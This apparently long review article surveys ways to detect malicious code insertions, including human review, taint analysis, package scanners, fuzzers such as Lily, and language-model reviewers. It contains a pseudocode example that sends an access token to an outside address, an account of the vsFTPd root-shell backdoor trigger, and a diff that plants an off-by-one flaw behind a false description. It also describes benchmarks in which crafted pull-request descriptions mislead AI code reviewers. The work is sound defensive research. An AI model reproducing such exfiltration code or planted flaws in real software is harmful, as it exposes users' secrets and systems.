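Wu and Lu sent their findings to the Linux community and summarised its response, but did not formally survey maintainers. The developers said that they fix code only when it goes wrong and would not accept patches for immature vulnerabilities. They acknowledged that patches can introduce bugs and that mistakes happen in a largely manual review, and pointed to the bug-finding tools that they and many companies run continually. They also said that the community depends on trust and would not assume that some contributors are malicious.

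The researchers' first proposal was to have contributors promise not to introduce bugs intentionally, but an attacker would make that promise too. Checking contributors' identities might do more. It could have hindered a pseudonymous maintainer like Jia Tan, but not an employee like Davis Lu, whose company knew who he was.

Wu and Lu's proposal to accept preventive patches for the riskiest immature vulnerabilities is more useful against trusted developers, because it removes weaknesses that any attacker could build on. It would also add to the work of maintainers who already have too many patches to read. Wu and Lu also recommend inviting more people to review patches, using static analysis that can follow aliases and concurrent code, and fuzzing the changed code while forcing errors to occur.

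### How much can three patches show?

Jones objects that three patches are too few for meaningful statistics. If each flawed patch independently had a 63% chance of getting through review, reviewers would still stop all three about 5% of the time (0.37³). So the board's finding that none got through is compatible with a review process that misses more than half of such patches. If all three had gotten through, the result would have been just as inconclusive, since that would happen about 5% of the time even if each patch had only a 37% chance.

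The study also had no control group. Wu and Lu could have sent matching sound patches from similar accounts and compared how often maintainers rejected each kind. Maintainers may have rejected a patch because they disliked its wording or distrusted an unknown sender, and the study can't rule this out without that comparison. It also can't provide a false-alarm rate.

Keeping the reviewers unaware made their behaviour more realistic, because people who expect a planted bug read more carefully. An LWN commenter notes that companies send their own staff fake phishing emails with senior management's approval. A project's leaders could approve a review test in the same way, so the whole organisation need not be deceived. But Wu and Lu had to step in as soon as a maintainer approved a patch, so even an approval would have given them evidence about only one early stage. They could not learn whether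 a second maintainer, an automated build or later testing would have caught the bug.

The experiment's main limitation as evidence about trusted developers is that the patches came from strangers. Wu and Lu excluded the kernel's own developers and maintainers from their threat model. A colleague's good reputation might lower a reviewer's guard, but the experiment does not show by how much. In the historical data, maintainers wrote 47.8% of minor patches in general and 37.3% of the minor patches that introduced vulnerabilities. Their patches therefore seem to have been somewhat safer than outsiders' patches, though far from guaranteed to be safe.

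### Consequences for human and automated review

The experiment and the board's findings don't establish how reliably human reviewers catch planted flaws. Rejecting a patch for the wrong reason is only a partial success for a defender, because the author can fix whatever the maintainer complained about and resubmit it with the planted bug still in place.

An attacker can also try again somewhere else. If reviewers catch each attempt with probability *c*, and the attempts are independent, at least one of *n* attempts succeeds with probability 1 − *cⁿ*. At the baseline catch rate of 56.6%, at least one of three attempts would succeed 82% of the time. This is only an illustration, because a maintainer who has caught one bad patch may read the next more carefully.

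Reading patches more carefully takes a lot of work. A commenter on Edge's article argues that checking whether a claimed bug is real means repeating the analysis that the patch's author supposedly did, which a volunteer project cannot do for every patch. Guenter Roeck, a kernel developer, told Lu that he had become much less willing to accept minor fixes from people he didn't know because of the affair. That is understandable, but it focuses suspicion on newcomers, and Jia Tan had become a familiar name over more than two years before adding the xz backdoor.

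The experiment provides even less evidence about automated review. Wu and Lu do not report running a detection tool on their three patches, and Sashiko, the kernel's AI reviewer, did not yet exist. They argue that detection would be difficult because most tools used for Linux could not follow indirect calls, in which the program chooses which function to call as it runs. Fuzzers also rarely reached error paths and had trouble with drivers, which make up 62% of the kernel's code and often need particular hardware. These are reasonable criticisms of the tools available in 2020, but they do not measure how often those tools would have detected the patches.

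The researchers' search programs could also help defenders. A project could keep a list of its immature vulnerabilities and warn the reviewer whenever a patch seems to add a missing condition. In the example above, the reviewer would learn that `disconnect` releases the device before the new line reads its name, which the diff does not show. With thousands of candidates, many harmless patches would probably trigger warnings too, and Wu and Lu did not test how many.

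The patch that led to the ban shows the harm false alarms can do. Aditya Pakki, who wrote it, had relied on a static analyser whose sensitivity, he admitted, was "obviously not great", and Kroah-Hartman mistook the result for sabotage. Qu has since built VulnBERT, a model intended to catch kernel bugs when a developer commits them. Testing such a model on the Minnesota patches would have the same weakness as the test on xz, because the patches have been public since 2021.

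## What can static analysis find in a malicious change?

The analyser that misled Aditya Pakki was static. Static analysers don't run the program, so they can check code that no test reaches, often within seconds. They therefore seem well suited to finding hidden triggers. Some search for suspicious patterns, and others follow sensitive data through a program. Related tools mostly compare a commit's author, timing and files with the project's history rather than analysing the code.

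### Pattern rules

A pattern rule describes code that a reviewer should check. A security engineer writes the rule, and the tool searches every file and lists the matching lines for the reviewer. To catch a backdoor like `log_in`, a rule could match any login function that compares the username with a fixed string.

The simplest rules match text, which leads to elementary mistakes. Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?*, found that Microsoft's OSSGadget scanner raised many false alarms because comments and documentation mentioned common download programs. Rules that use the structure of the code avoid this because they distinguish function calls from text that mentions them.

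Even an accurate match is little evidence of the code's purpose. A function that runs system commands can build a program or give an intruder control of the machine. Guo and colleagues call this the gap between capability, which is what code can do, and intent.

GuardDog, a free scanner from Datadog, combines rules to look for malicious code in packages, the bundles of code that developers install from registries such as npm (for JavaScript) and PyPI (for Python). According to Datadog's *Introducing GuardDog 3.0* (2026), some rules identify capabilities, such as making network connections, and others identify warning signs, such as the names of files that hold passwords. GuardDog looks for places where a capability and a warning sign occur together, and gives the package a risk score out of 10. How severe the worst risk is and how specific the matched code is to malware each count for 30%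 of the score, while how complete and how sophisticated the attack is each count for 20%. Datadog considers a package that scores above 7 likely to be malicious, but treats a single match as only a weak signal.

Datadog dropped GuardDog's older rules partly because they fitted known malware so closely that they missed new examples. A rule that flags obfuscated code doesn't have to match known malware. *S3C2 Summit 2025-07* (2026) reports that participants said they might struggle to unscramble obfuscated code but could still tell it was obfuscated. A project that normally accepts only readable code can reject such a change without working out what it does.

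### Taint analysis

Code that steals data can look harmless on every line, so a rule that checks one place at a time may miss it. Taint analysis instead follows the data from source to destination. The data might be an access token, which works like a password for programs and lets whoever receives it act as its owner.

```
function refresh_session():
    token = read_secret("ACCESS_TOKEN")
    report = make_json("session", token)
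    post(OUTSIDE_ADDRESS, report)
```

The source is `read_secret`, whose return value the tool marks as tainted. The path runs through `token`, which holds that value, and `report`, which `make_json` builds from `token`. The destination is `post`, which sends `report` to an outside address. The tool raises an alarm because tainted data has reached a network call, and it shows the path.

Programs also send tokens over the network for good reasons, mostly to log in to other services, so a team usually gives the tool a list of approved destinations. If `OUTSIDE_ADDRESS` is on the list, the tool raises no alarm, even though the data takes the same path. The tool cannot detect who reads the data after it arrives. A trusted developer may also be allowed to edit the list, so changes to it need at least as much review as changes to the code.

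The alarm can also disappear if the data passes through code that the tool does not model. Suppose that `make_json` comes from an outside library that the tool cannot read. If the tool assumes that the result no longer contains the token, it stops tracking the data and raises no alarm when `post` sends it. If it assumes that the result still contains the token, it keeps this alarm but also raises many false ones about legitimate uses of the library.

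Existing static analysis tools miss some malicious code. Guo and colleagues tested GENIE, whose rule for detecting theft of system information requires at least three kinds of information to reach the same web request. The rule misses a program that sends only one or two kinds, or that uses another channel. Some newer malware sends the data through a separate system command, so a tool that checks only for network functions does not find where the data goes.

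Taint analysis works for any data that a team can label as sensitive, including model weights.

### Why perfect detection is impossible

Rice's theorem, which Henry Gordon Rice published in 1953, concerns questions about what programs do when they run. No program can answer such a question correctly for every program, unless the answer is the same for all of them. The theorem applies to the question "Does this program ever send the token to an outsider?" because some programs do and others don't.

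To see why, suppose someone has built a perfect detector of leaked tokens and gives it this function, where `other_program` sends nothing itself.

```
function puzzle():
    run(other_program)
    send(access_token, OUTSIDE_ADDRESS)
```

The function leaks the token only if `other_program` finishes. To be right every time, the detector would have to work out, for any program we put there, whether it will finish. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no program can do this in every case, so a perfect detector cannot exist.

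This rules out a tool that always gives an answer and is never wrong. A tool can still be right about most real code and answer "not sure" about the rest, or it can flag everything that might leak a token. It can also check simpler things, such as whether a diff contains the word `post`, because Rice's theorem doesn't cover questions about text. A team can also insist on code that is simple enough to analyse. Honest developers seldom need a function like `puzzle`, so "not sure" is a good reason to ask the author for a simpler version.

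A reviewer could know exactly what the code does and still not know whether it was permitted. For example, a function that deletes customer records may be sabotage, or it may carry out the customers' own requests.

### How well do package scanners work?

Guo and colleagues ran 11 scanners, some in several variants, on 6,420 malicious and 7,288 harmless npm packages. Four static scanners show the range of results. The false-alarm rates here are calculated from the published precision and detection rates.

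| Scanner | Detection rate | False-alarm rate |
|---|---|---|
| Packj (static mode) | 98.7% | 85.5% |
| OSSGadget | 91.6% | 79.3% |
| GuardDog | 89.9% | 2.5% |
| GENIE | 46.1% | 0.1% |

Packj flags any package that uses one of 56 listed functions, so it flags nearly all malware but also most harmless packages. GENIE needs much stronger evidence to flag a package, and it misses more than half of the malware. GuardDog did best of the four tools, which Guo and colleagues attribute to its use of taint analysis and a list of install scripts known to be harmless.

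GuardDog's precision in this test was 97%, but nearly half the packages were malicious. At a company with 10 malicious and 10,000 harmless changes, the same detection and false-alarm rates would produce about 9 correct alarms and 246 false ones, for a precision of 3.5%. The false-alarm rate might be somewhat lower in practice, because the harmless packages in the test were popular, and popular packages tend to set off more alarms.

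About 80% of the malicious packages used no technique to evade detection, and 72% relied on install scripts, which npm runs automatically when someone installs a package. Two of GuardDog's 22 rules, one for install scripts and one for suspicious links, accounted for over 90% of its detections. A trusted developer can weaken a login check without using an install script or a suspicious link. Guo and colleagues sorted the packages by behaviour rather than author, so they give no detection rate for trusted authors.

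Detection rates varied widely with the type of behaviour. GuardDog caught more than 94% of the packages that sent out data or ran system commands, but only 7% of those that assembled and ran new code at runtime. The scanners as a group also detected credential theft poorly, because legitimate login libraries use the same functions. They were most effective when suspicious behaviours occurred together. The average detection rate was 40.0% for collecting data and 72.2% for sending it out, but 85.4% for packages that did both.

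The results may slightly overstate GuardDog's performance, since the experts who checked the labels used it and OSSGadget to find the code to read. The results also apply to an older version, whose rules Datadog has since replaced. *Towards Robust Detection of Open Source Software Supply Chain Poisoning Attacks* (2024) reported a similar detection rate of 94% for GuardDog on Python packages. *MalGuard* (2025) traced GuardDog's false alarms to certain kinds of function that the tool flagged as suspicious wherever they appeared.

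Detectors used to raise far more false alarms. *A Benchmark Comparison of Python Malware Detection Approaches* (Vu, 2022) measured false-alarm rates of 15% to 97% in the tools of the time, while package registry operators said that even 0.01% would be too high. The detector in *One Detector Fits All* (2025) came much closer to what they wanted. In a 37-day live trial, it checked 91,949 PyPI packages and found an average of 2.48 malicious ones a day, with 2 false alarms a day. Its precision was about 55%, even though only about one package in a thousand was a confirmed attack. Nobody knows how many attacks it missed. The trial also covered newly published packages, which are a different problem from edits by an established colleague.

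### Passwords and triggers written into the code

A hard-coded credential is a password or key written directly into a program. Scanners look for known formats, such as the fixed opening letters of some cloud service keys, or for random-looking text next to words like "password". Biringa and Kul (2025), in *Detecting Hard-Coded Credentials in Software Repositories via LLMs*, point out that scanners using such rules can miss a credential that departs slightly from the expected format. They used two older language models, BERT and GPT-2, to convert each credential into a list of numbers, which a second program used to sort the credentials into eight types. Their best model beat the previous best tool by 13% on F1, a score that combines detection rate and precision.

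Biringa and Kul define these credentials as accidental, so their result concerns honest developers who forgot to remove a secret. It doesn't cover crude malware or a login planted by a trusted author. The name "special-guest" in `log_in` doesn't look like a secret, so a scanner for leaked keys would be unlikely to flag it.

Stringer is a static tool that searches compiled programs for fixed strings likely to trigger a backdoor. In *ROSA*, Kokkonis, Marcozzi and colleagues (2025) ran it on 17 programs, 7 with authentic backdoors and 10 with backdoors planted by researchers. Stringer found part of the trigger in only 4 programs, and left an average of 308 strings per program for someone to inspect. It missed a fixed login planted in sudo, the standard Linux tool for running commands with administrator rights.

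Four of the authentic backdoors came from the manufacturers of the routers that contained them, so the people who wrote them were presumably authorized to change the code. Stringer found none of these four. The two authentic backdoors it did find came from attacks on the PHP programming language and the file server ProFTPD. This result is discouraging, and there is little other direct evidence on trusted authors. But the sample is tiny, and Stringer had to work without the source code, where meaningful names and comments would have made a strange comparison easier to notice.

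### Anomaly scores from commit metadata

Even when malicious code looks ordinary, the circumstances in which someone added it may be unusual. *Anomalicious* (Gonzalez, Zimmermann and colleagues, 2021) presents a tool that uses a project's whole history to establish what is normal for the project and for each author, then checks every commit against a set of rules. Some rules test whether the commit touches sensitive files such as build settings, whether the author has edited those files before, and whether the change is unusually large. Others use the author's record, including the number of earlier commits and the share of pull requests that the project rejected. The tool flags a commit if it breaks a large enough share of the rules.

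One test case was event-stream, a popular JavaScript package. In 2018, a contributor who had been given extra rights by the owner added a malicious package as a dependency. The commit modified three files, two of them sensitive, while the contributor's average was 1.31 files. The commit broke a third of the rules, just enough for the tool to flag it.

Anomalicious found 8 of 15 malicious commits. But 13 of the 15 were infections by Octopus Scanner, malware that spreads from a developer's computer into their projects, so most of the named authors were probably victims. The tool caught 6 of the 13 commits by authors it rated as trusted, and both commits by the other two authors. It missed a commit in which an employee of a software company added pop-up advertisements to minimap, an add-on for a text editor.

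The tool's low alarm rate comes from a separate test on 100 projects with no known malicious commits. It flagged fewer than 5% of commits in 99 of them and fewer than 1% in 56. But in that test, a commit had to break half of the rules to be flagged. The event-stream commit would not have reached that threshold, so the 53% result and the low alarm rate come from different settings. Gonzalez and colleagues also chose the lower threshold, used for the 53% result, after trying several on the same malicious commits, which makes that figure somewhat optimistic.

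A newer detector replaces the handwritten rules with a neural network. *Detecting Backdoors in Collaboration Graphs of Software Repositories* (Ganz, Ashraf and colleagues, 2023) represents a project as a graph linking developers, commits, files and functions. The model learns what ordinary connections look like, with the help of artificial anomalies made by swapping authors, times or messages between commits. It then scores each new commit by how far it departs from that pattern.

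This detector found the malicious code in 15 of 19 repositories, including all 11 infected by Octopus Scanner. It found 4 of the other 8: event-stream, PHP, and two repositories of the Linux distribution Gentoo that attackers had broken into. In the PHP case, an intruder posing as a maintainer committed malicious code at around 6 a.m., although the real maintainer's last 20 commits had all come after 6 p.m. The four misses included minimap and the browser extension The Great Suspender. Ganz and colleagues say that the maintainers planted those two backdoors themselves, so the commits' authorship gave little sign of an attack.

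The false-alarm rate is less certain. Averaged over the repositories, it was 10.75%, the figure Kokkonis and colleagues cite when criticizing the detector. Very small projects inflate this average, including one with 15 commits where the detector flagged 71% of the harmless ones. Ganz and colleagues prefer the rate over all 6,656 commits, which they give as 0.70%, or 47 false alarms. But the rates they list for the individual repositories imply about 154 false alarms, or 2.3%. Precision in the test would then be about 9% rather than the 24% implied by their count. Kokkonis and colleagues wanted to test the detector themselves but could not get its code to run on a modern system.

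Metadata is more useful against impostors. In *Stylometric Defenses Against Author Impersonation in Software Repositories*, Ravich and Fire (2026) trained a model on more than 20 years of Linux kernel history. The model compares the style of a commit's code and message with the same account's earlier work, and it ranked both forged PHP commits in about the top 1% of commits to review. A developer who adds a backdoor from their own account would write in their own style and might easily pass this check.

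Jia Tan's history contains some clues. *Towards Socio-Technical Topology-Aware Adaptive Threat Detection in Software Supply Chains* (2025) found that the malicious xz commits came at unusual times of day, and *Beneath the Mask* (Nealon, 2025) found odd patterns in the account's contributions to other projects. Both studies began with a known culprit. Picking out such an account in advance is much harder, because many honest volunteers also keep irregular hours.

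### Which insertions does static analysis find?

Static analysis is most reliable at detecting open payloads that resemble known malware and code that sends a known secret directly to an unapproved address. GuardDog's detection rate of over 94% for packages that send out data supports this, although most of the attackers behind those packages were not trying to hide. An open payload made of everyday operations is harder to detect, because a scanner will flag `delete(customer_records)` only if someone has configured it to treat those records as important.

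Static analysis sometimes finds explicit backdoors. The PHP backdoor took text from a visitor's request and ran it as a program, so a taint rule covering the function that ran the text could have caught it. Stringer did find the trigger, though among 573 strings. Ganz and colleagues argue that no static analyser would have flagged the backdoor as insecure without knowing its context, which seems too pessimistic. Static analysis also finds only some of the exfiltration logic that uses an approved service or passes through code the tool does not model.

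It is less clear how well static analysis finds deliberate vulnerabilities. A tool could catch the faulty comparison in `get_page` if it had the document's page count, and *ROSA* notes that established bug-finding tools can detect flaws planted on purpose. But *ROSA* gives no detection rate, and none of the 11 malicious behaviours in the npm benchmark is a planted flaw. Tools will probably catch some common mistakes inside a single function. They are likely to miss flaws that depend on distant code or on the timing of concurrent tasks more often, as human reviewers do.

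Static analysis rarely finds a backdoor that is assembled only after the analysis runs, as in xz, where the source code looked clean. The xz payload also modified code in memory at runtime, which *ROSA* describes as hard for static tools to handle.

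## Can running the changed code reveal a hidden backdoor?

A backdoor that escapes static analysis still has to do something when the attacker uses it. Dynamic analysis runs the program and records what it does, however innocent the source code looks. To catch a backdoor this way, a tool has to produce an input that triggers it and then detect that the program's behavior is unusual.

Fuzzing can find the input that triggers a backdoor. A modern fuzzer starts from a few sample inputs, changes them at random, and keeps any changed input that reaches new code. It then repeats the process with the inputs it kept to reach code deeper in the program. Fixed passwords used to stop fuzzers, because guessing all 13 characters of "special-guest" at once could take 256¹³ attempts, or about 2 × 10³¹. Newer fuzzers can split the comparison into single characters and keep an input when it gets one more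 of them right. In the ideal case, they need at most 13 × 256 = 3,328 attempts.

Noticing the backdoor is harder, because fuzzers normally check for crashes and a well-made backdoor doesn't cause one. But a program can't open a file, use the network or start another program without making a request to the operating system, known as a system call. A backdoor that gives its owner access to the machine must therefore make system calls, which a tool can record.

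### Comparing similar inputs

*ROSA* presents the first tool to use fuzzing to find backdoors. The tool, also called ROSA, relies on the idea that similar inputs should have similar effects. For example, every wrong password given to sudo should produce an error message. If one makes sudo run the command instead, the system calls will differ. ROSA first fuzzes the program for a minute to collect ordinary inputs. It then fuzzes for hours and matches each new input with the ordinary one that took the most similar path through the code. If the two caused different types of system call, ROSA reports the new input.

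ROSA was tested on Rosarum, the same set of 17 backdoors in which Stringer found only four. A colleague who had not worked on ROSA planted nine of the ten artificial ones, so the tool's developers had no prior knowledge of those nine. ROSA found all 17 at least once and succeeded in 156 of 180 eight-hour runs, after an hour and a half on average. In all 24 failed runs, the fuzzer never produced the trigger. Someone also had to check an average of seven reports per backdoor, which took about two minutes each.

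ROSA did well on the four backdoors from router manufacturers, which are the closest in the set to the work of trusted developers. It caught three of them in every run. The fourth was in a Belkin router, and ROSA missed it in all ten runs with standard sample inputs. When the researchers supplied samples aimed at web addresses, ROSA found it in seven of ten runs.

A check that takes hours and nearly always raises a false alarm is acceptable for a one-time audit of a router, but developers would soon switch it off if it ran on every commit.

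### Comparing two versions

Kokkonis and colleagues designed ROSA's successor, Lily, for CI, where fuzzing usually gets about ten minutes per change. Lily compares the new version of a program with the old one, which it assumes to be clean. For each input, it records a profile, meaning the set of system-call types that the input causes. The rule for flagging an input is short:

```
normal = profiles of saved inputs, run on new_version

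for each input the fuzzer keeps during ten minutes:
    p = profile(new_version, input)
    if p is not in normal and profile(old_version, input) != p:
        flag(input)
```

The saved inputs come from fuzzing the previous version. Lily runs them on the new version because an honest change may alter the program's normal behavior. For example, if a developer makes a server log every request, the saved inputs will also be logged, so Lily will raise no alarm.

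Comparing the new version with the old one filters out behaviour that is rare but not new. A talk on Lily, *automatic backdoor detection in ci*, gives the example of a request to PHP's web server that announces an impossibly large upload. The server's refusal produces an unusual profile, but the old version refuses the request in the same way.

When Lily flags an input, it lists the changed lines that ran on that input and traces the unusual system calls back to the lines that made them. The reviewer also gets the input and can use it to reproduce the behaviour.

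Lily treats the old version as clean, so it can't find a backdoor that was there before the project adopted Lily. Kokkonis and colleagues suggest auditing the program with ROSA first.

### A smiley face in vsFTPd

vsFTPd is a file server whose official download contained a backdoor for a few days in 2011. Moore (2011), in *vsftpd download backdoored*, quotes an estimate that someone introduced it between 30 June and 1 July. If a visitor entered a username containing ":)", the server opened a root shell, a command line with full control of the machine. Debian's *CVE-2011-2523* records that the distribution's own package was not affected.

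Kokkonis and colleagues gave Lily the infected release and the previous one. The fuzzer produced a username containing ":)", and the server waited for a network connection and prepared to start a shell. Lily flagged the input because none of the saved inputs had caused that combination of system calls, and the old version did not produce it when given the same username. The full diff covered 1,407 lines in five files, but Lily's report highlighted seven lines in one file. Anyone who knows C can see from those lines that the server offers a shell to whoever connects.

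Checking the archive's digital signature would also have worked here, and is much simpler. Chris Evans, who wrote vsFTPd, found that the archive did not match his signature, according to a post that Shnurapet quoted in *vsftpd in the news* (2011). A signature check would not have stopped Jia Tan, who could sign xz releases.

### Detection and false alarms

Kokkonis and colleagues ran the main test on the 13 open-source programs in Rosarum. They planted each program's backdoor in one commit and in the newer version of each of 50 pairs of releases, most of which had shipped with Debian or Ubuntu. The harmless changes were 432 real commits and the same 50 pairs without the backdoors. Lily checked every change 20 times, for ten minutes each time.

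| Type of change | Backdoored runs flagged | Harmless runs flagged |
|---|---|---|
| Commits | 233 of 260 (90%) | 17 of 8,640 (0.2%) |
| Releases | 828 of 1,000 (83%) | 43 of 1,000 (4.3%) |

At these per-commit rates, Lily would raise 9 correct alarms and about 20 false ones a year at the example company with 10 malicious and 10,000 harmless changes. Its precision would be 31%, compared with 3.5% for GuardDog. This comparison favors Lily because it assumes that all ten malicious changes are backdoors like those in the test, in programs that a fuzzer can run.

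The low false-alarm rate depends on using both parts of the rule. Kokkonis and colleagues repeated the harmless runs with each part alone:

| Lily flags a profile if it is | False alarms on commits | False alarms on releases |
|---|---|---|
| abnormal for the new version | 14% | 20% |
| absent from the old version | 10% | 58% |
| both | 0.2% | 4.3% |

A release combines months or years of work, so much of its behaviour is new and innocent. This could also be a problem for *Preflight* (2026), which checks new versions of the outside packages an application uses. Preflight takes the functions the application calls, runs them in both the new version and a reference version, and mainly looks for security-sensitive capabilities that only the new version has. It checks for a narrower range of behaviour than Lily does, so it may raise fewer false alarms than the middle row suggests.

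Lily's reports stayed short even for large releases. The two PHP releases in a pair differed by more than two million lines on average, but the report highlighted 11.

### What repeated runs add

Because fuzzing is random, one run may miss a backdoor that the next one finds. Lily's detection rate was lowest on a commit to libsndfile, a sound library, where it caught the backdoor in 13 of 20 runs, or 65%. At that rate, two independent runs would catch it with probability 1 − 0.35² ≈ 88%, and three with probability 96%. Across all 13 backdoored commits, a second run would raise the average detection rate from 90% to about 97%.

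False alarms also accumulate over repeated runs, though less evenly. Lily flagged 1.6% of the harmless commits (7 of 432) at least once in 20 runs, compared with 0.2% in a single run. A project that ran Lily 20 times and blocked a commit after any alarm would therefore wrongly block about eight times as many commits as one that ran it once. Four of the seven flagged commits were very large merges in PHP, and a maintainer could learn to expect false alarms on those.

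Lily flagged 5 of the 50 harmless releases (10%) at least once in 20 runs. If the false alarms had been independent, a rate of 4.3% per run would have led it to flag 58% of them. Two libsndfile releases set off an alarm in every run and accounted for 40 of the 43 false alarms. Running Lily again will clear an occasional false alarm, but somebody has to investigate one that recurs every time.

### Would Lily have stopped the real attacks?

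Kokkonis and colleagues claim that Lily could have prevented the real vsFTPd, ProFTPD and PHP incidents. According to CERT-Renater's *ProFTPD Compromise Report* (2010), attackers broke into the main distribution server for ProFTPD, another file server, on 28 November 2010 and replaced the source files. A user noticed on 1 December. Debian's *CVE-2010-20103* describes the backdoor as a hidden command that let anyone run programs with full control of the server.

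The PHP attacker pushed two malicious commits to the project's repository, one under the name of Nikita Popov, a maintainer, and the other under that of Rasmus Lerdorf, PHP's creator. Popov (2021) reported the commits on 28 March 2021 and later told the PHP mailing list that the attacker had logged in with passwords, possibly taken from a leaked user database.

When Kokkonis and colleagues reproduced the attacks, Lily detected the vsFTPd backdoor in all 20 runs, the PHP one in 16 and the ProFTPD one in 14. A single ten-minute run would probably have stopped each attack, but would have missed the ProFTPD backdoor three times in ten. The researchers also tested the full sequence of PHP commits, in which someone removed the backdoor and the attacker then restored it. Lily flagged both insertions in 80% of runs and did not flag the removal. Kokkonis and colleagues describe the removal as part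 of the attackers' disguise, but Popov reports having reverted the first commit on noticing it.

The claim is reasonable about what the method can detect, but less convincing about whether it would have caught the two file-server attacks at the time. They happened years before Google launched OSS-Fuzz in 2016, and somebody would have had to prepare the file-server programs for fuzzing.

All three attackers were outsiders who had gained unauthorized access. Lily's results don't depend on who wrote a change, so it should produce the same result for the same code from a trusted developer. However, a trusted developer may know which parts of the program the fuzzer reaches.

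### Code the fuzzer does not reach

A fuzzer feeds generated inputs to the software through a small program called a harness, which largely determines which code the fuzzer can reach. Across 337 commits that changed code in 12 projects, Kokkonis and colleagues found that the fuzzer ran about 32% of the changed lines on average. Every backdoor in their test set off an alarm at least once, so all of them were in code the fuzzer could reach. If a backdoor were equally likely to be in any changed line, and Lily caught 90% of those in the lines it reached, it would catch only about 29% overall (0.9 × 0.32).

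That estimate may be too pessimistic for a well-maintained project today, because many of the commits were old and had only early harnesses. Kokkonis and colleagues write that modern harnesses typically cover such changes almost completely, though they give no figure. Poor harnesses also explain Lily's weakest results, detection rates of 39% to 43% on releases of libpng, libsndfile and ProFTPD. *Large-Scale Empirical Analysis of Continuous Fuzzing* (2025) examined about 1.12 million OSS-Fuzz sessions and found that coverage keeps rising as a project continues to fuzz. New code may still lack a suitable harness at first.

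Language models may shorten that wait. *Understanding Gaps in LLM Pipelines Towards Scalable Fuzzing Harness Generation* (2025) presents HarnessAgent, which produced working harnesses for more than 80% of the functions it attempted, at an average cost of about 22 cents per success. HarnessAgent still does not reliably distinguish real bugs from false alarms.

Better harnesses won't help a fuzzer activate a backdoor whose trigger needs a secret key, as the xz backdoor's did. For this reason, the researchers left xz out of Rosarum, and they do not claim that Lily would have stopped it. The speaker in the talk on Lily argued that a cryptographic check leaves a large gap in the coverage report, which the contributor then has to explain. That gap would be a useful warning in a project with nearly complete coverage, but it is unlikely to attract attention where the fuzzer already misses two-thirds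 of the changed lines.

Kokkonis and colleagues simulated another form of evasion, which cut Lily's detection rate to about half. A stricter mode restored the rate but raised false alarms to 2.5% of commit runs and 18% of release runs.

### Harm without an unusual system call

Lily is a poor check for deliberate vulnerabilities because they do nothing unusual until someone exploits them. Suppose the fuzzer uses `get_page` to request page 10 of a ten-page document. The program reads the wrong part of its own memory and returns the contents. This requires no system call, so the profile is the same as for any other page. An attacker might later use the flaw to start a shell, but that would take a carefully constructed input that a fuzzer is unlikely to generate in ten minutes.

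Ordinary fuzzing is better suited to this flaw. Developers can build the program with a sanitizer, which adds checks to memory accesses and stops the program when it reads outside the document. The fuzzer can then expose the flaw just by requesting page 10, without producing a working exploit.

Comparing the values inside a program across versions can also reveal flaws. *Enhancing Code Review through Fuzzing and Likely Invariants* (2025) presents FuzzSight, which looks for rules that appear to hold whenever the program runs, such as "n is always less than the page count". It then points the reviewer to code where these rules changed between versions. FuzzSight flagged 75% of regression bugs (faults that a change introduces into working code) and up to 80% of the vulnerabilities that 24 hours of fuzzing had uncovered. Both percentages cover only bugs that fuzzing could already find, so they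 don't measure how many deliberate vulnerabilities FuzzSight would miss.

Lily's design also makes it unsuitable for open payloads. If a change makes the program delete customer records on every run, the saved inputs will trigger the deletion too, so it will become part of the new version's normal behaviour. Exfiltration can be equally hard to detect in a program that already reads files and uses the network, because a profile records the types of system call but not what data the program sends or where. Taint analysis is a better check for exfiltration.

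## How well do language models judge malicious changes?

Static rules and fuzzers don't use the reason an author gives for a change. A language model can read that reason next to the code and judge whether the two fit together, as a human reviewer would. It can also detect a flaw like the one in `get_page`, which causes no unusual system call. However, a malicious author can use the stated reason to influence the model's verdict.

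### From pull request to verdict

A language-model reviewer is an ordinary program built around a model. When a developer opens a pull request, the program builds a prompt from its standing instructions, the diff and usually the title and description. The model may output its findings immediately, or it may first output a request for more context, such as the rest of a changed file or every place that calls a certain function. The program fetches that context, adds it to the prompt and runs the model again. Once the model outputs its findings, the program turns them into an approval, a rejection or a comment.

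In *SEVRA-BENCH*, Melo, Fogliato and colleagues (2026) built a simple reviewer of this kind. They tell the model that it is a code reviewer and must read every changed file, and they let it decide whether to look further. The model has ten functions for tasks such as searching the code, listing the commits and reading earlier comments. One of them approves and merges the change. If the model finishes without calling that function, the change is not merged.

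*From Verdict to Diagnosis* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) presents PRGuard, which has a model propose possible vulnerabilities and then check each one against the code in the repository. A fixed rule then blocks the change if the evidence supports at least one vulnerability, leaves a comment if the evidence is incomplete, and otherwise approves the change. In one test with GPT-5.5, PRGuard described the real flaw in 54 of 63 malicious changes but blocked only 43 of them. A maintainer who read the comments would therefore have learned of flaws in some changes that PRGuard did not block.

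A reviewer can try to establish whether the code is flawed, whether the description matches it, and whether the author is acting in bad faith. Suppose a developer submits this change to `get_page`:

```
Description: Tidy up the page check. No change in behaviour.

  function get_page(document, n):
      # pages are numbered from 0
-     if n >= 0 and n < document.page_count:
+     if n >= 0 and n <= document.page_count:
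          return document.pages[n]
```

The change introduces the off-by-one error described earlier, and its description is wrong because the behaviour has changed. Neither fact proves bad faith. Many honest developers write careless descriptions of sound code, and a malicious change can have an accurate description.

### Old flaws in new pull requests

SEVRA-BENCH tests reviewers on real vulnerabilities. Melo and colleagues collected 150 commits that each fixed a publicly known vulnerability. They then applied each fix in reverse to the fixed version of the project, which brought the original flaw back. The flaws belong to ten classes from a list of the most dangerous software weaknesses, including use-after-free and SQL injection, in which text from a visitor becomes part of a database command.

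Two language models then wrote 15 pairs of titles and descriptions for each change, each pair presenting it as legitimate in a different way, which produced 2,250 pull requests from 150 diffs. To save money and concentrate on hard cases, Melo and colleagues first ran two cheap models, Claude Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5.4-nano, and kept only the 1,062 pull requests that at least one of them approved. Eight models, including those two, each reviewed the remaining pull requests once.

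Because of this selection, the rejection rates do not apply to malicious changes in general. The comparison is also slightly biased against the two cheap models, since which changes stayed in the test depended on their mistakes.

Melo and colleagues left any mention of security out of the prompt to see whether a model would raise security concerns in an ordinary review.

### Rejecting a vulnerability as an ordinary bug

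Melo and colleagues report two figures for each model. The rejection rate is the share of malicious pull requests that the model declined. The security reason rate counts only rejections in which the model identified the underlying exploit, according to another language model that read its explanation.

Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.5 gave the security reason in over 80% of cases involving SQL injection or code injection. For use-after-free flaws, the kind Wu and Lu tried to plant in Linux, they gave it in only 30% and 20% of cases, respectively. The models often still rejected these changes, but as ordinary bugs. They described the invalid use of memory correctly without explaining what an attacker could do with it.

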